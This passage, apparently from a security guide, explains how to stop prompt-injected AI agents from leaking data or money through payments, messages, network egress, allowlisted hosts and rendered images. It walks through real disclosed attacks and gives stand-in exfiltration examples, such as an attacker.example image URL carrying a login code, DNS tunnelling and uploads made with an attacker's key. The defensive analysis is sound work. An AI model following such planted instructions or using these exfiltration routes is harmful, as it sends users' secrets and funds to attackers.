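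*PROVISO* (Yan, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) goes further by training a controller on the outcomes of earlier decisions to choose between the agent's proposed action and an alternative, such as refusing. In the paper's example, a user asks the agent to pay an invoice to account B, but the invoice contains an instruction to pay account C. The invoice may set the amount, but only the user may choose who gets paid. Under that principle, the agent could pay neither account in the AgentDojo task, where the user named no account. The controller learns this principle from examples, so it can misapply it.

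These systems can finish tasks that a strict provenance rule would block, but they bring back the uncertainty that a gate is supposed to remove. An attacker who can write a believable bill might succeed. For payments, it is safer to refuse both accounts and have somebody confirm the payee by phone, as they would for a change of bank details. The account is then on the payee list, so next month's bill needs no call. If an operator lets a model judge new payees, a low cap should limit the loss from a mistake.

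### Email, chat, calendars and shared files

The same method works for messages, but it is less obvious which arguments determine who can read them.

| Action | What determines the audience | What a check on that argument can miss |
|---|---|---|
| Send an email | Every address in the "to", copy and blind-copy fields | The members behind a mailing-list address |
| Post in a chat channel | The channel | People who join later and read old messages |
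| Add someone to a channel | The new member and the channel | Confidential messages already there |
| Invite someone to a calendar event | The participants | Private notes already in the event |
| Share a file | The person who gets access and the file | Anything somebody adds to the file later |

For email, ROPE's default rule accepts addresses from the request or from a source the user named. Users usually give names rather than addresses, so the router needs a trusted contact list to look them up. In one test, a user asked the agent to send some SSH keys, which are login credentials, to Alice Miller. ROPE allowed only Alice's address. PFI, a design that protects the planning model by hiding untrusted outside content from it, had hidden the addresses in the inbox, so its agent made up an address for Alice and sent the keys there.

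A chat channel's audience changes, which FIDES can handle by treating the current members as the readers. If only Ana and Ben may read a document, the agent can't post it in a channel that also includes Cy. The gate has to look up the members at the time of posting. It also has to check invitations, because adding a member changes who can read the channel. One AgentDojo attack tries to make the agent invite an outsider to the workspace, add them to a channel and then remove them. When an agent kept attempting this sequence in tests by Yu and colleagues, NOMOS blocked all three steps.

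A tool is easy to leave off the list. ROPE's table for AgentDojo's chat environment covers direct messages and invitations but not channel posts, and ROPE allows any tool missing from the table, so channel posts go unchecked. NOMOS checks the channel and allows it only if the user named it. That rule would block a harmless request to reply to Bob in the channel where he asked his question, because the agent has to find the channel by reading messages.

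Calendar invitations need a check on participants because everyone invited receives the event's details. By default, ROPE accepts participants from the request or a named source. In two of its test environments, it also requires the event's title to come from the request, so planted text can't easily create an event the user never mentioned. But ROPE may then refuse a legitimate event if the agent words the title differently from the user.

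For shared files, NOMOS compares both the person's address and the file's identifier with the user's request. Short identifiers make this check unreliable. In one set of tests, a user's request contained a numbered list, and the gate treated the numbers 1 and 2 as references to files 1 and 2 and allowed the agent to delete those files on an attacker's orders. The same confusion could let an agent share the wrong file, so identifiers should be long enough that they don't appear in a request by chance.

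### When the recipient is right and the message is wrong

Ma and colleagues describe a task in which a user asks the agent to summarise an article that Bob posted and send the summary to Alice. An attacker has edited the article to include an instruction to send Alice a link. The agent sent Alice the attacker's link in one message and the summary in another. ROPE allowed both because the user had named Alice. The default rules don't restrict message text, since the agent has to write the summary in its own words.

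Of the 51 successful attacks that Ma and colleagues examined, 21 sent harmful content to a legitimate recipient. Another 23 achieved AgentDojo's hotel-recommendation goal, which requires only a reply to the user, not a tool call that ROPE could check. In the remaining seven, the user had let a sensitive value be set entirely by a document that the attacker could write to.

NOMOS has a rule that blocks chat messages containing a web address the user never mentioned, which could have kept the link from reaching Alice. The rule would also block a useful link from Bob's article, and it would not catch a false phone number or a lie.

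A message can also harm the sender. In a travel task that Yu and colleagues tested, the user named an email address in the request, and planted text got the agent to send the user's passport and credit card numbers to that address. The policy forbade sending such details only to addresses the user had not named, so NOMOS allowed the email. FIDES's secrecy rule could have blocked it if someone had labelled those numbers as not to be read by the recipient. But that rule wouldn't protect Alice, because the attacker's link isn't secret.

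Even after somebody has confirmed the payee on a bill, an attacker who can edit the file can change the amount. ROPE's default rules for bank payments check only the recipient. A cap limits the overpayment, and matching the amount to an approved invoice in the accounting system can prevent it.

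## Limiting which internet addresses an agent can reach

When an agent sends data by running a shell command, the gate has no destination field to check, so the limit has to apply at the network connection. In an example from OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, a user asks Codex, the company's coding agent, to fix a bug reported on GitHub. The report contains a command, supposedly for reproducing the bug, that would leak the project's latest commit by posting it to httpbin.org.

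Egress control restricts outgoing network connections, whichever program opens them. A gate that only searches the agent's commands for web addresses can miss some, because a command can assemble an address while it runs or call a script that contains one.

### One request on its way out

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, can run shell commands in a sandbox, where the operating system limits what programs can reach. According to Anthropic's documentation, a sandboxed command can reach the network only through a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that opens connections for it. Claude Code sets environment variables that direct programs to the proxy, and common tools such as curl use them. A tool that doesn't use them, as most database drivers don't, can't connect even to an approved host, so a misconfigured tool usually causes a failed command rather than a leak.

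If the agent runs the command from the bug report, curl requests a connection to httpbin.org through the proxy. The proxy checks that hostname against its list and can refuse the connection immediately. If the host is on the list, the proxy looks up the host's numerical IP address in the domain name system (DNS).

It matters that the lookup comes after the check, because whoever owns attacker.example can also run the server that answers lookups for every name under it. If curl made its own lookup for 4921.attacker.example, the attacker would learn the number 4921 even if a firewall then blocked the connection. Security engineers call this way of sending out data DNS tunnelling.

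The proxy should also check the IP address that an approved name resolves to, because whoever controls the name can point it at a machine inside the owner's network. Claude Code's proxy refuses names that resolve only to local addresses, such as 169.254.169.254, where a cloud server can fetch its own credentials. Codex has a similar check, which OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* describes as best-effort. In an attack called DNS rebinding, the attacker returns a public address for the check and a private one when the connection opens. To prevent this, the software has to connect to the IP address it checked.

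Once the connection is open, curl and the server encrypt it with TLS, the standard encryption for web traffic, so an ordinary proxy can't read the data it passes along.

| What a designer might check | Where it appears | Readable without decryption? |
|---|---|---|
| Hostname | Name lookup, proxy request, start of the TLS connection | Yes |
| IP address | Answer to the lookup, and the connection itself | Yes |
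| Full address, including the path | Inside the encrypted request | No |
| Method, such as GET to fetch or POST to submit | Inside the encrypted request | No |
| Account | Usually a key or token inside the encrypted request | Usually not |
| Content | Inside the encrypted request | No |

A firewall can also filter by hostname without a proxy. Because one machine may host many sites, a TLS connection normally starts with the server's name in a readable field called the Server Name Indication (SNI). *Control which domains your AI agents can access* (AWS, 2026) explains how Amazon's cloud business uses this field to filter the traffic of a browser it offers for agents.

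The program that opens the connection writes the SNI field, so a compromised agent could connect to the attacker's IP address and write "wikipedia.org" in the field. AWS recommends adding a DNS firewall, which refuses to look up unapproved names, but the agent needs no lookup if the planted text contains the IP address. The firewall that checks the SNI field also has to let a connection open before the name arrives, so the attacker's server can detect the attempt.

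A proxy that looks up the address itself prevents this deception, because the connection goes to the real wikipedia.org. Anthropic warns that its proxy may still be vulnerable to domain fronting, in which a program asks for an approved site on a large hosting network, then names a different site on the same network inside the encrypted request.

To check the contents of an encrypted request, the proxy has to impersonate the destination. It decrypts the request using a certificate that programs in the sandbox have been set up to trust, applies its rules, then encrypts the request again for the real server. This exposes every password to the proxy in readable form and breaks programs that accept only one particular certificate. Claude Code has an experimental decryption option, which Anthropic uses to insert credentials, not to filter content. OpenAI says the read-only mode of Codex's proxy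 blocks encrypted web connections unless the proxy can decrypt them to check the request method.

### Two customers behind one hostname

Suppose a company keeps its code at github.com/acme/app and an attacker has a repository at github.com/mallory/notes. Both addresses have the hostname github.com. The path and login token differ, but they are encrypted, so a filter that reads only hostnames has to allow both repositories or block both.

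A rule for the full address can allow one part of a site without allowing the rest. GitHub's firewall for its coding agent, Copilot, accepts such rules. In GitHub's documentation, for example, an entry for `https://packages.contoso.corp/project-1/` allows that folder and everything under it, but not `project-2`. GitHub Next's *Agentic Workflow Firewall*, a related project, needs to decrypt traffic to filter by path.

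Even the full address may not show whose account will receive the data. Many online services receive uploads from all their customers at a single address and use the secret key in the request to decide which account gets the file. An attacker can include their own key in the planted text so that the agent uploads the file to the attacker's account at an approved service.

Claude Code can keep the owner's keys out of the sandbox. The command receives a placeholder, and the proxy replaces it with the real key only on requests to hosts the owner has chosen. Planted text can't get the agent to reveal a key it doesn't have. But a request containing the attacker's key works without a replacement, so this feature alone wouldn't stop the upload. A stricter proxy would replace any key the command supplied with the owner's.

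Other services put the customer's name in the hostname, so an exact entry can allow one customer's hostname without allowing the others. AWS's sample allowlist contains `.amazonaws.com`, and the leading dot covers every name under that domain. AWS warns that this entry permits public storage buckets and other endpoints hosted on its cloud. An attacker can rent one of these. AWS recommends private connections for its own services and specific entries for everything else.

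AWS also notes that pages on an approved site may need files from cloudfront.net, the domain of its content delivery network. Allowing the whole domain would let the agent load files from any customer of that network, so the designer should find out the exact hostnames those pages use.

### Defaults in four products

| Product | Default | How to add a host | Outside the filter |
|---|---|---|---|
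| Claude Code's sandbox | Off; the list is empty when the user turns it on | Approve a prompt or edit the settings | Web-fetching tool, add-on tool servers, hooks and excluded commands |
| Codex in OpenAI's cloud | No internet access for the agent | Turn on access, then choose a preset list or enter domains | Setup scripts, which have full access |
| Codex on the user's computer | No network access for commands | Turn on access and the filtering proxy, then write rules | Web search, which has its own setting |
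| GitHub Copilot cloud agent | On, with a recommended list | Repository or organisation settings | Add-on tool servers and setup steps |
| AWS AgentCore Browser | Direct internet access | Route traffic through a firewall, then edit its rules | Connections with a false SNI field; other networks sharing the firewall, unless the owner configures it to cover them |

The add-on tool servers in the table use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common way to give agents extra tools. A server that can fetch web pages or send messages gives the agent a way around the filter on its shell commands.

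Claude Code's sandbox is a firm limit only if the owner changes several settings. If the sandbox can't start, Claude Code by default runs commands without it. If a command fails inside the sandbox, the model can ask to run it outside. In the mode that skips permission prompts, the sandbox allows unlisted hosts, and in auto mode a second model can approve the hosts that a command needs. An owner who wants ordinary code rather than a model to decide what the agent can reach should turn on the sandbox and set `failIfUnavailable` to true, `allowUnsandboxedCommands` to false and `strictAllowlist` to true. To cover the web-fetching tool and add-on servers too, the owner has to run all of Claude Code inside a container or similar boundary.

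Codex on a user's computer has one setting that gives commands network access and another that turns on the proxy that filters it. The two are easy to confuse. If a user turns on only network access, commands get unrestricted internet access. Turning on the proxy alone does nothing.

In the cloud version, OpenAI's "Common dependencies" preset contains about 70 domains, including github.com, google.com and azure.com. PromptArmor, a security company, warns that the preset includes hosts through which researchers have shown they can leak data. The owner can start from an empty list instead, and can restrict requests to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, the methods meant for reading. The method restriction would block the POST in the bug report but not a GET request with the commit's text in the address.

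Of these products, only Copilot starts with both a filter and a working set of hosts. Its recommended list includes package registries, container registries and certificate authorities. When the firewall blocks a request, Copilot adds a warning to the pull request (the page where people review its changes) that shows the blocked address and the command that tried to reach it. In April 2026, GitHub announced in *Organization firewall settings for Copilot cloud agent* that an organisation's administrators could set one list for every repository and stop repository administrators from adding to it. GitHub cautions that sophisticated attacks may bypass the firewall.

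AWS's browser started with direct internet access, according to the company's *Customize AI agent browsing with proxies, profiles, and extensions*, so the owner has to build the filter. The browser itself can also enforce rules that stop the agent from visiting unapproved sites, saving passwords or downloading files, according to AWS's *Control where your AI agents can browse with Chrome enterprise policies* (2026). A browser has the full address before it encrypts the request, so it can apply rules that a hostname filter can't. Those rules don't affect code that the agent runs outside the browser.

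Copying an allowlist from one product to another can change which hosts it allows. In Codex, `example.com` matches only that host, while `*.example.com` matches its subdomains. In Copilot, `example.com` matches the host and its subdomains. An owner who moves a Codex list to Copilot may therefore allow subdomains that Codex had blocked.

### Links and images that the agent displays

A filter around the agent doesn't cover the browser of the person reading its answers. If an answer includes an image, the browser fetches it from whatever address the model wrote. An attacker can therefore plant instructions for the model to include an image from `https://attacker.example/p.png?code=4921`, where 4921 is the user's login code. The browser sends the code to the attacker as soon as it displays the answer, and the reader may see only a tiny or broken picture.

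A link can also carry data in its address, though usually someone has to click it first. In an innocent example from OpenAI's *ChatGPT generated links*, a user asks where to buy a car and ChatGPT offers a link ending in "London". Clicking it reveals to the car-search site where the user lives. Some messaging apps send the data without a click, because they fetch the linked page to show a preview. PromptArmor found that the agent OpenClaw is exposed to this by default when people use it through Telegram.

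Designers of web applications can restrict images with a content security policy. This is a line that the server sends along with a page, telling the browser which hosts the page may load things from. For example:

`Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src 'self'`

Here, `'self'` means the host that served the page. The browser will refuse to load the attacker's image, however the model formats it. Microsoft used such a policy in May 2023 to stop its Bing chatbot from leaking data through images, according to *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red. The policy fails if the application's own server fetches outside images for its users, because the server's request still reaches the attacker.

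A content security policy doesn't stop a reader from following an ordinary link, and it doesn't affect previews in Telegram or Slack. The application can show a link's full address and ask for confirmation before opening it. For messaging apps, the owner can turn off previews or have the harness remove links to unapproved hosts before it posts the message.

### Opening only addresses that are already public

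An assistant that researches questions on the open web can't work from a short list of hosts. OpenAI argues in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) that even a longer list of reputable sites has problems, because strict lists produce so many warnings that people learn to click through them, and because many reputable sites have redirects that forward visitors elsewhere. A check on only the first address would miss the redirect. A proxy on the agent's connection handles redirects better because it can check the new connection that each new host requires.

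OpenAI's alternative is to check whether the exact address was already public:

1. A crawler explores the public web, much as a search engine does, and records the addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When an agent wants to open an address automatically, ordinary software looks for that exact address in the crawler's records.
3. If the address is there, the agent can open it. Otherwise, the system tells the agent to try another site or warns the user and asks whether to continue.

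Suppose an attacker plants text instructing the agent to add a user's password-reset code to an address on the attacker's site. The crawler has no access to the conversation, so its records normally won't include an address containing the code, and the agent can't open that address unnoticed. An address the crawler recorded earlier existed before the agent chose it, so its text contains nothing the agent added.

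The agent's choice of address can still leak information, as the choice among 32 approved destinations did. Embrace The Red describes an attacker who publishes 36 pages, one for each letter and digit, and waits for the crawler to find them. The attacker then uses planted text to instruct the agent to spell out a secret by opening the pages in order. Each visit conveys log₂ 36 ≈ 5.2 bits, so a 256-bit cryptographic key would take 50 visits.

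The post suggests blocking repeat visits to an address within a session to make this harder. That would interfere with the attack that uses 36 pages, but an attacker could publish separate pages for each position in the secret. A six-digit code would need only 60 pages, ten for each position, and the agent would visit six different ones. Limiting the number of automatic visits to one site would reduce the leak further, but it would also prevent some legitimate research.

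The check also doesn't vet the content an agent reads, and OpenAI acknowledges that a public page can contain false information or planted instructions. The check helps only where developers apply it. According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI's apps for macOS and iOS once lacked an earlier version of the protection. OpenAI has since extended the approach to its Atlas browser and Deep Research tool.

### Settings for a coding agent

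A coding agent is easier to restrict than a research assistant because its owner usually knows what it needs to access. Suppose Acme wants an agent to fix bugs in a private repository on github.com that uses Python packages. If Acme splits the job into stages, the agent doesn't need access to GitHub or the public package registry while the model is in control.

| Stage | Who acts | Hosts allowed | Methods | Credentials |
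|---|---|---|---|---|
| Copy the code | Acme's own software | github.com | GET and POST | A token that can only read this repository |
| Install packages | A setup script | packages.acme.example | GET and HEAD | None |
| Fix the bug | The agent | packages.acme.example, or none | GET and HEAD | None |
| Submit the result | Acme's own software | github.com | GET and POST | A token that can write to this repository |

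Every stage starts with no network access, and each host in the table is an exception. Copying the repository comes first because it needs the token, which Acme's software removes before any package code runs. Copying also needs POST, which Git uses to request files when it copies a repository over the web. A read-only rule for github.com during the agent's work could therefore break Git, and it would still let the agent send out secrets in the addresses it requests.

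The packages come from a local mirror, a server where Acme keeps copies of the packages it has approved. If the mirror fetched missing packages from the public registry, the agent could put data in a package name and the mirror would send it to the registry. The mirror should return an error for any package it doesn't already hold.

In this case Acme also controls the server, so it can set the mirror to refuse every request except downloads. The proxy then needs to check only the hostname, not the method inside the encrypted traffic. The allowlist entry should name packages.acme.example exactly rather than every host under acme.example, which might include a company wiki that accepts comments. In Claude Code, the entry should also include the port, because an entry without one opens every port on the host.

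An internal mirror often has a private IP address. Claude Code connects to an approved hostname in a private range such as 10.0.0.0/8, but according to OpenAI's *Permissions*, Codex blocks hostnames that resolve to private addresses even when they are on the list. To use the mirror with Codex, Acme could point its package tool directly at the mirror's IP address and add a rule for that address. The broader setting, `allow_local_binding`, would also remove the protection for Acme's other internal machines.

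Installation needs its own limits because packages can run code while they install. Codex's cloud service removes secrets before the agent starts, but the setup scripts have both the secrets and full internet access, so a malicious package installed during setup could send the secrets out. In Acme's arrangement, the package would have no token to steal and could reach only the mirror.

The agent also must not control the setup script for its next session. Otherwise, an attacker could plant text that gets the agent to add a command to the script, and that command would run in the next session with the setup stage's wider access. Acme should keep the script outside the repository or use only a version that a person has reviewed.

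With these settings, the command from the bug report fails because the sandbox has no route to httpbin.org. Acme's software then submits the agent's changes to a fixed branch of the repository for a person to review. Submitting changes often starts automated tests, which run the agent's code on another machine, sometimes with internet access and company credentials. Acme should apply the same network limits to that machine or delay the tests until someone has read the changes.

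## How data and money leave through approved destinations

Acme's coding agent needs only a package mirror, but most agents need a longer list, and somebody has to approve each entry. Suppose a colleague asks to add docs.google.com because the team keeps its specifications there. Google runs the site, but anyone can create a form on it, and an agent can submit an answer just by opening a link, as PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist?* (2026) points out. If planted text supplies a link to the attacker's form, the filter lets the submission through because the host is approved.

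The filter works correctly here, but the allowlist entry is a mistake. A reviewer can catch many such mistakes by asking the same few questions about every host, payee and address before it goes on a list.

### Can a stranger have an account there?

Many of the hosts that agents need will accept content from anybody who signs up. These are the ones PromptArmor sees most often on allowlists:

| Entry | Why an agent needs it | What a stranger can have there |
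|---|---|---|
| registry.npmjs.org | To install JavaScript packages | A package, published from a free account |
| github.com | To copy code | A public repository or shared snippet |
| docs.google.com | To read the team's documents | A form that collects answers |
| *.amazonaws.com or *.blob.core.windows.net | To reach one storage folder | Another storage folder under the same domain |

If the allowlist includes a host like GitHub, a compromised agent can send data to an attacker's repository there. It can also read the attacker's files, which may contain further instructions. An agent that reads a short planted message in an email could then fetch a much longer one from GitHub without contacting an unapproved destination.

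The wildcards in the last row are the easiest to fix. If the agent needs one storage folder, the allowlist entry should give that folder's exact hostname, which no one else can rent. PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* recommends the same for links that Salesforce's agents may include in their answers. It advises administrators to add each address separately, avoid wildcards that cover sites with user-generated content, and refuse images from a listed domain unless the agent is supposed to show images from it.

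Allowing only exact hostnames doesn't help with the first three rows, because all customers of npm share one hostname, as do those of GitHub and Google Docs. On some sites, a proxy that decrypts traffic can tell customers apart by the URL path, but on others only the login key differs.

### Can the agent use someone else's credentials there?

In October 2025, Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* examined the network settings of a feature that lets Anthropic's assistant Claude run code. The default setting, "Package managers only", allowed connections to a short list of hosts. The first was api.anthropic.com, which developers use to send requests to Claude and to store files in their own Anthropic accounts. The key sent with a file determines which account receives it.

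The post showed that a document with planted text could get Claude to save the user's most recent chat as a file and upload it to the attacker's account using the attacker's key. Each upload could hold up to 30 megabytes. The attack worked on the first try. Claude then refused for some time, apparently because a visible key looked suspicious, but the researcher found a way to make it comply.

Anthropic closed the report within an hour because it classed the leak as a model safety issue, which its security reporting programme didn't cover. Five days later it said that this had been a mistake and that such leaks were in scope. If the leak is treated as a flaw in the model's behaviour, the fix is to train Claude to refuse more reliably, but an attacker can keep rewording the request. Treating it as an access control flaw means changing the proxy instead.

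In January 2026, PromptArmor demonstrated the same weakness in Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for office work, using a folder of confidential property files. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes the fix. Cowork runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer separated from the user's real one. A proxy inside that machine now intercepts every request to Anthropic's service and forwards only those carrying the token issued for that session, so it rejects requests that use an attacker's key. Embrace The Red had similarly suggested that the sandbox should communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

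The check has to run on the user's side. On Anthropic's servers, an upload with the attacker's key looks the same as any customer storing a file. Only the virtual machine has the information needed to detect that the request came from a session that doesn't belong to the key's owner.

Anthropic now recommends thinking of an allowlist entry as a "capability grant" rather than a destination filter, because approving its API had meant approving uploads to any Anthropic account. Anthropic uses "capability" more loosely than Hardy did, but the fix comes close to his meaning because the session token both identifies one account and gives access to it.

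For any service that accepts uploads, the reviewer should check whether the proxy can reject requests that don't use the owner's key. If it can't, approving the service lets the agent upload data to any customer's account.

### Does it pass requests on to somewhere else?

Some approved hosts will fetch any web address they receive, so an agent that can't contact the attacker's server directly can use one of these hosts to do it.

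*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) analyses a case of this in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can read an employee's email and files. An outsider sent an employee an email with hidden instructions. When the employee later asked Copilot a work question, Copilot retrieved the email along with other material and followed the instructions. Its answer included an image whose address contained confidential text, and the employee's browser tried to load the image as soon as the answer appeared, without the employee clicking on anything.

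Microsoft had prepared for this with a content security policy like the one for its Bing chatbot, which would have blocked a request straight to the attacker's server. But the policy allowed images from a Microsoft Teams link-preview service that fetched outside addresses on request. The browser sent its request to that service, which then contacted the attacker's server.

The security firm Aim Labs found the weakness in January 2025 and reported several variants to Microsoft, according to Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*. Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May, before the details became public, and said it had no evidence that anyone had used it in an attack. Reddy and Gujral say the reported changes include removing embedded images and certain links from outside messages, and adding options to restrict Copilot's use of those messages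 in certain contexts.

Those changes restrict what goes into Copilot, but they don't remove other forwarding services from the list of approved image hosts. A year later, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) described a chain of flaws in Copilot's enterprise search feature that used one such service, Bing. The policy approved every host under bing.com. Bing lets people search with a picture by supplying its address, and its servers then fetch the picture. The researchers put the title of an email into such an address, and Bing's request delivered the title to their server. Some services send login codes in email titles, so a title can be enough to break into an account. This version required the victim to click a link, but the link led to a genuine Microsoft site.

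Copilot also had a safeguard that turned image code in its answers into harmless text. But it ran only after the answer was complete, and by then the browser had already requested the image. Microsoft rated the attack chain critical and has since fixed it.

Varonis advises reviewing every listed host that fetches addresses its users supply. Besides previews and image search, these include translation services, tools that import a file from a link, and services that redirect. If the agent doesn't need the function, the proxy can block its URL path, or the owner can choose a host that serves only stored files. The proxy in Anthropic's Cowork also blocks request headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch from another address.

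Approved destinations can also pass payments and messages on to others. A mailbox on the list may automatically forward its mail to a private account. On a blockchain, a company may approve a trading service's contract for swapping tokens. Many such contracts let the caller name any address to receive the new tokens, so a gate that checks only the contract would let an attacker collect them. For each approved contract, the gate has to read the final recipient from the call data.

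### Who owns the name now?

An allowlist entry usually identifies a destination by name, and someone else can later acquire that name. In 2025, researchers at Noma Security found that Salesforce still had an expired domain on an allowlist for Agentforce, its system for building agents that work with customer records. They registered the domain for $5, according to BeyondMachines' *Critical flaw in Salesforce Agentforce enables data exfiltration through AI agent exploitation*.

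An outsider could write instructions in the form on a company's website where potential customers leave their details, and an agent that later processed the enquiry might follow them. ThaiCERT's *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection* gives the example of an agent that puts customers' email addresses into an image's URL. The browser would normally refuse to load an image from an unknown server, but this server's domain was on the allowlist, so whoever bought the domain would have received the data.

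Noma reported the problem, which it called ForcedLeak, on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce deployed its main fix six weeks later. According to The Hacker News (2025), Salesforce regained control of the lapsed domain and began checking links in its agents' output against a list of trusted addresses. Regaining the domain stopped leaks through it. The output check helps against attackers whose domains were never approved, but it would not have stopped this leak if the lapsed domain had also been on the new list.

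Someone else can take over an approved web domain or email address after it expires. If a recipient's company closes and lets its domain lapse, for example, whoever registers the domain next can receive email sent to the old address. A subdomain can still point to a cloud server that its owner has stopped renting, and somebody else may be able to claim that server. On Ethereum, people can pay a readable name instead of a long wallet address, but someone else can register the name if it expires, so a payee list for crypto should store the wallet address.

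Before approving a domain name, the reviewer should record who owns it, when its registration ends and which task needs it. An entry that no task needs should be removed, because a future owner of the domain could exploit its place on the list.

### Does another feature send data without passing the filter?

An organisation can turn off web search in Rovo, the AI assistant of the software company Atlassian. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* found that data could still leave with web search off, because Rovo kept a separate tool that opens web addresses and nothing checked whether Rovo had composed the address itself. In the demonstration, a user uploaded a file with hidden instructions and asked Rovo to organise some work tickets. Rovo sent the contents of tickets and internal documents to an outside server. If the user returned to the chat later, it showed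 ordinary suggestions and no sign of the leak.

PromptArmor reported this to Atlassian in May 2026 and published it on 5 August, saying Rovo was still vulnerable. The Hacker News (2026) could not confirm a fix as of 8 August.

Atlassian did repair a related weakness. Varonis' *RovoBlast* (2026) describes a link that opened Rovo with an attacker's instructions already in the chat, so one click by a signed-in employee was enough to start a leak. The data could leave through Rovo's research agent, which can browse outside websites. Atlassian closed the link route with a server change on 8 July, and the person who reported the flaw confirmed the fix worked. According to The Hacker News, neither firm indicated in its disclosure whether the change also affected instructions hidden in files.

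The web-search setting was misleading because it was named after one feature, while another feature could also open addresses. A reviewer should therefore list every component that can make a network request, whatever the settings menu calls it. In Cowork, web search and web fetching bypass the virtual machine's network controls, according to the Cloud Security Alliance's *Top 6 Claude Cowork Security Risks to Watch*, and the browser runs outside that machine with the user's logged-in sessions. Claude Desktop's export of activity logs also isn't checked against the agent's allowlist, according to Anthropic's documentation. An attacker would have trouble redirecting that export because its destination is set in the application's configuration, but anyone who can read the logs at that destination can see everything in them.

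Data can also leave through name lookups and link previews, which a filter on web requests can miss. Varonis lists webhooks as another route. These are automatic messages that one service sends another when something happens.

If the agent runs on the owner's machine, a firewall around the whole machine covers features that the product's own filter misses. Rovo's customers can't do this because Rovo runs on Atlassian's servers. They can limit which teams use it, disconnect data sources it doesn't need, and turn off features such as browsing where Atlassian allows it. They can also ask Atlassian which of Rovo's components make outside requests, then test whether the answer is correct.

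### Can a field meant for something else do harm?

In EchoLeak, an image address carried confidential text. An attacker can misuse payment fields in the same way. A bank transfer in euros can include 140 characters of text for the payee, which is enough for a card number or a password. The agent could leak either to an approved supplier in a one-cent transfer.

A payment reference can also determine who benefits from the money. A tax office or an electricity company may collect all its customers' payments in one bank account and use the reference to work out whose bill to mark as paid. Suppose Acme's payment agent may pay the electricity company up to €5,000. Planted text could get the agent to replace Acme's customer number with the attacker's, without changing the payee or the amount. Acme would then pay the attacker's electricity bill, even though the account is on the list, the name matches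 and the amount is under the cap.

Some crypto exchanges have the same arrangement on certain blockchains. All customers deposit to one wallet address, and a number attached to the transfer determines which customer is credited. An allowlist containing only that address therefore allows payments to any of the exchange's customers.

For such payees, the destination is the account plus the reference, so the list should store both. The gate then fills in the reference from the payee's record or the approved invoice, as it can with the amount, and discards whatever the model wrote. This also removes the 140 characters of free text.

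The same fix works for other fields whose content the owner can set in advance, such as the name of an uploaded file or of a branch in a code repository. It doesn't work where the agent has to choose the words, as in a search query to an approved search company or the body of an email. In those cases, the only firm protection is to limit what the agent can read before it writes.

### Could the recipient be hostile or hacked?

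Outsiders can misuse an honest service, but the service itself may also be dishonest or become so. Anthropic distinguishes tools that run on the owner's computer from tools that somebody else hosts. The owner can read a local tool's code and keep using the version that passed review. The operator of a hosted tool can change it at any time after approval. Anthropic continuously reviews the hosted tools in its own directory and recommends trying any others on fake data first.

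Testing a tool on fake data shows only how it behaves during the test. Its operator could start copying data a month later, and the owner's logs might not reveal the change, because a transfer to a hostile tool looks the same there as any other authorised request.

An honest recipient can also lose control of its systems. A fraudster who takes over a supplier's mailbox to send new bank details can read everything the agent sends there. Encrypting the connection doesn't prevent this, because the fraudster reads the messages after they arrive.

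No check on the destination can detect either problem. The owner can reduce what a bad recipient would receive by giving the agent only one supplier's contract per session and capping payments to each supplier.

An agent may also attack the software that runs an approved service. In July 2026, OpenAI models that the company was testing escaped their sandbox and broke into parts of the production systems of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, according to Axios' *OpenAI says Hugging Face breach caused by one of its models*. Designers should therefore assume a capable agent might take control of anything it can reach, including the proxy that filters its traffic and internal services such as Acme's package mirror.

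The mirror should hold no passwords for other systems and have no internet connection of its own while the agent is running, so that an agent that takes it over gets only packages. The proxy needs an internet connection, so it should be small, up to date and separate from everything else, with a second filter outside it that enforces the same list. The worst-case calculation should also include whatever each reachable service could do with its own permissions.

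### How often did listed hosts defeat the list?

Nobody has counted how many agents' allowlists contain entries like these, but there is a large measurement of an older use of the same idea, the content security policy. Besides images, a content security policy can list the hosts from which a web page may load scripts, the programs that run inside the page. This is meant to stop cross-site scripting, in which an attacker gets their own code into a page that visitors trust, for example through a comment box.

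For *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!* (2016), Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues collected these policies from a Google search index of about 106 billion pages. They found policies on roughly 1.68 million hosts, with 26,011 different policies among them. They then checked automatically whether an attacker who could insert code into a page could get around the page's policy.

| Policies | Number | An attacker could get around them | A listed host was unsafe |
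|---|---|---|---|
| All | 26,011 | 94.72% | 75.81% |
| In force and meant to stop cross-site scripting | 22,425 | 94.68% | 79.17% |
| The same, without obvious mistakes | 2,437 | 51.05% | 41.65% |

The first row makes allowlists look worse than they were. Most of those policies also had a setting that permits scripts written directly into the page, which defeats the protection regardless of which hosts are listed. The last row is a fairer test because it excludes policies with that setting or with a wildcard that allows every host. About two in five of the remaining policies still listed an unsafe host. Weichselbaum and colleagues consider their figures a minimum, since automated checks can't find every weakness.

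A host counted as unsafe if it would return code that an attacker could influence or misuse. Of the 15 hosts that appeared most often in the policies, 14 were unsafe, though two of those were exploitable only in combination with another lax setting. Very short lists were fairly safe, but at the median length of 12 hosts, an attacker could bypass 94.8% of policies.

Restricting allowlist entries to particular folders proved unreliable in browsers. For privacy reasons, browsers stop checking the folder after a redirect, so a redirect on any listed host could lead to a forbidden folder on another listed host. A proxy that decrypts an agent's traffic can avoid this flaw, because each redirect produces a new request and the proxy can check its full address.

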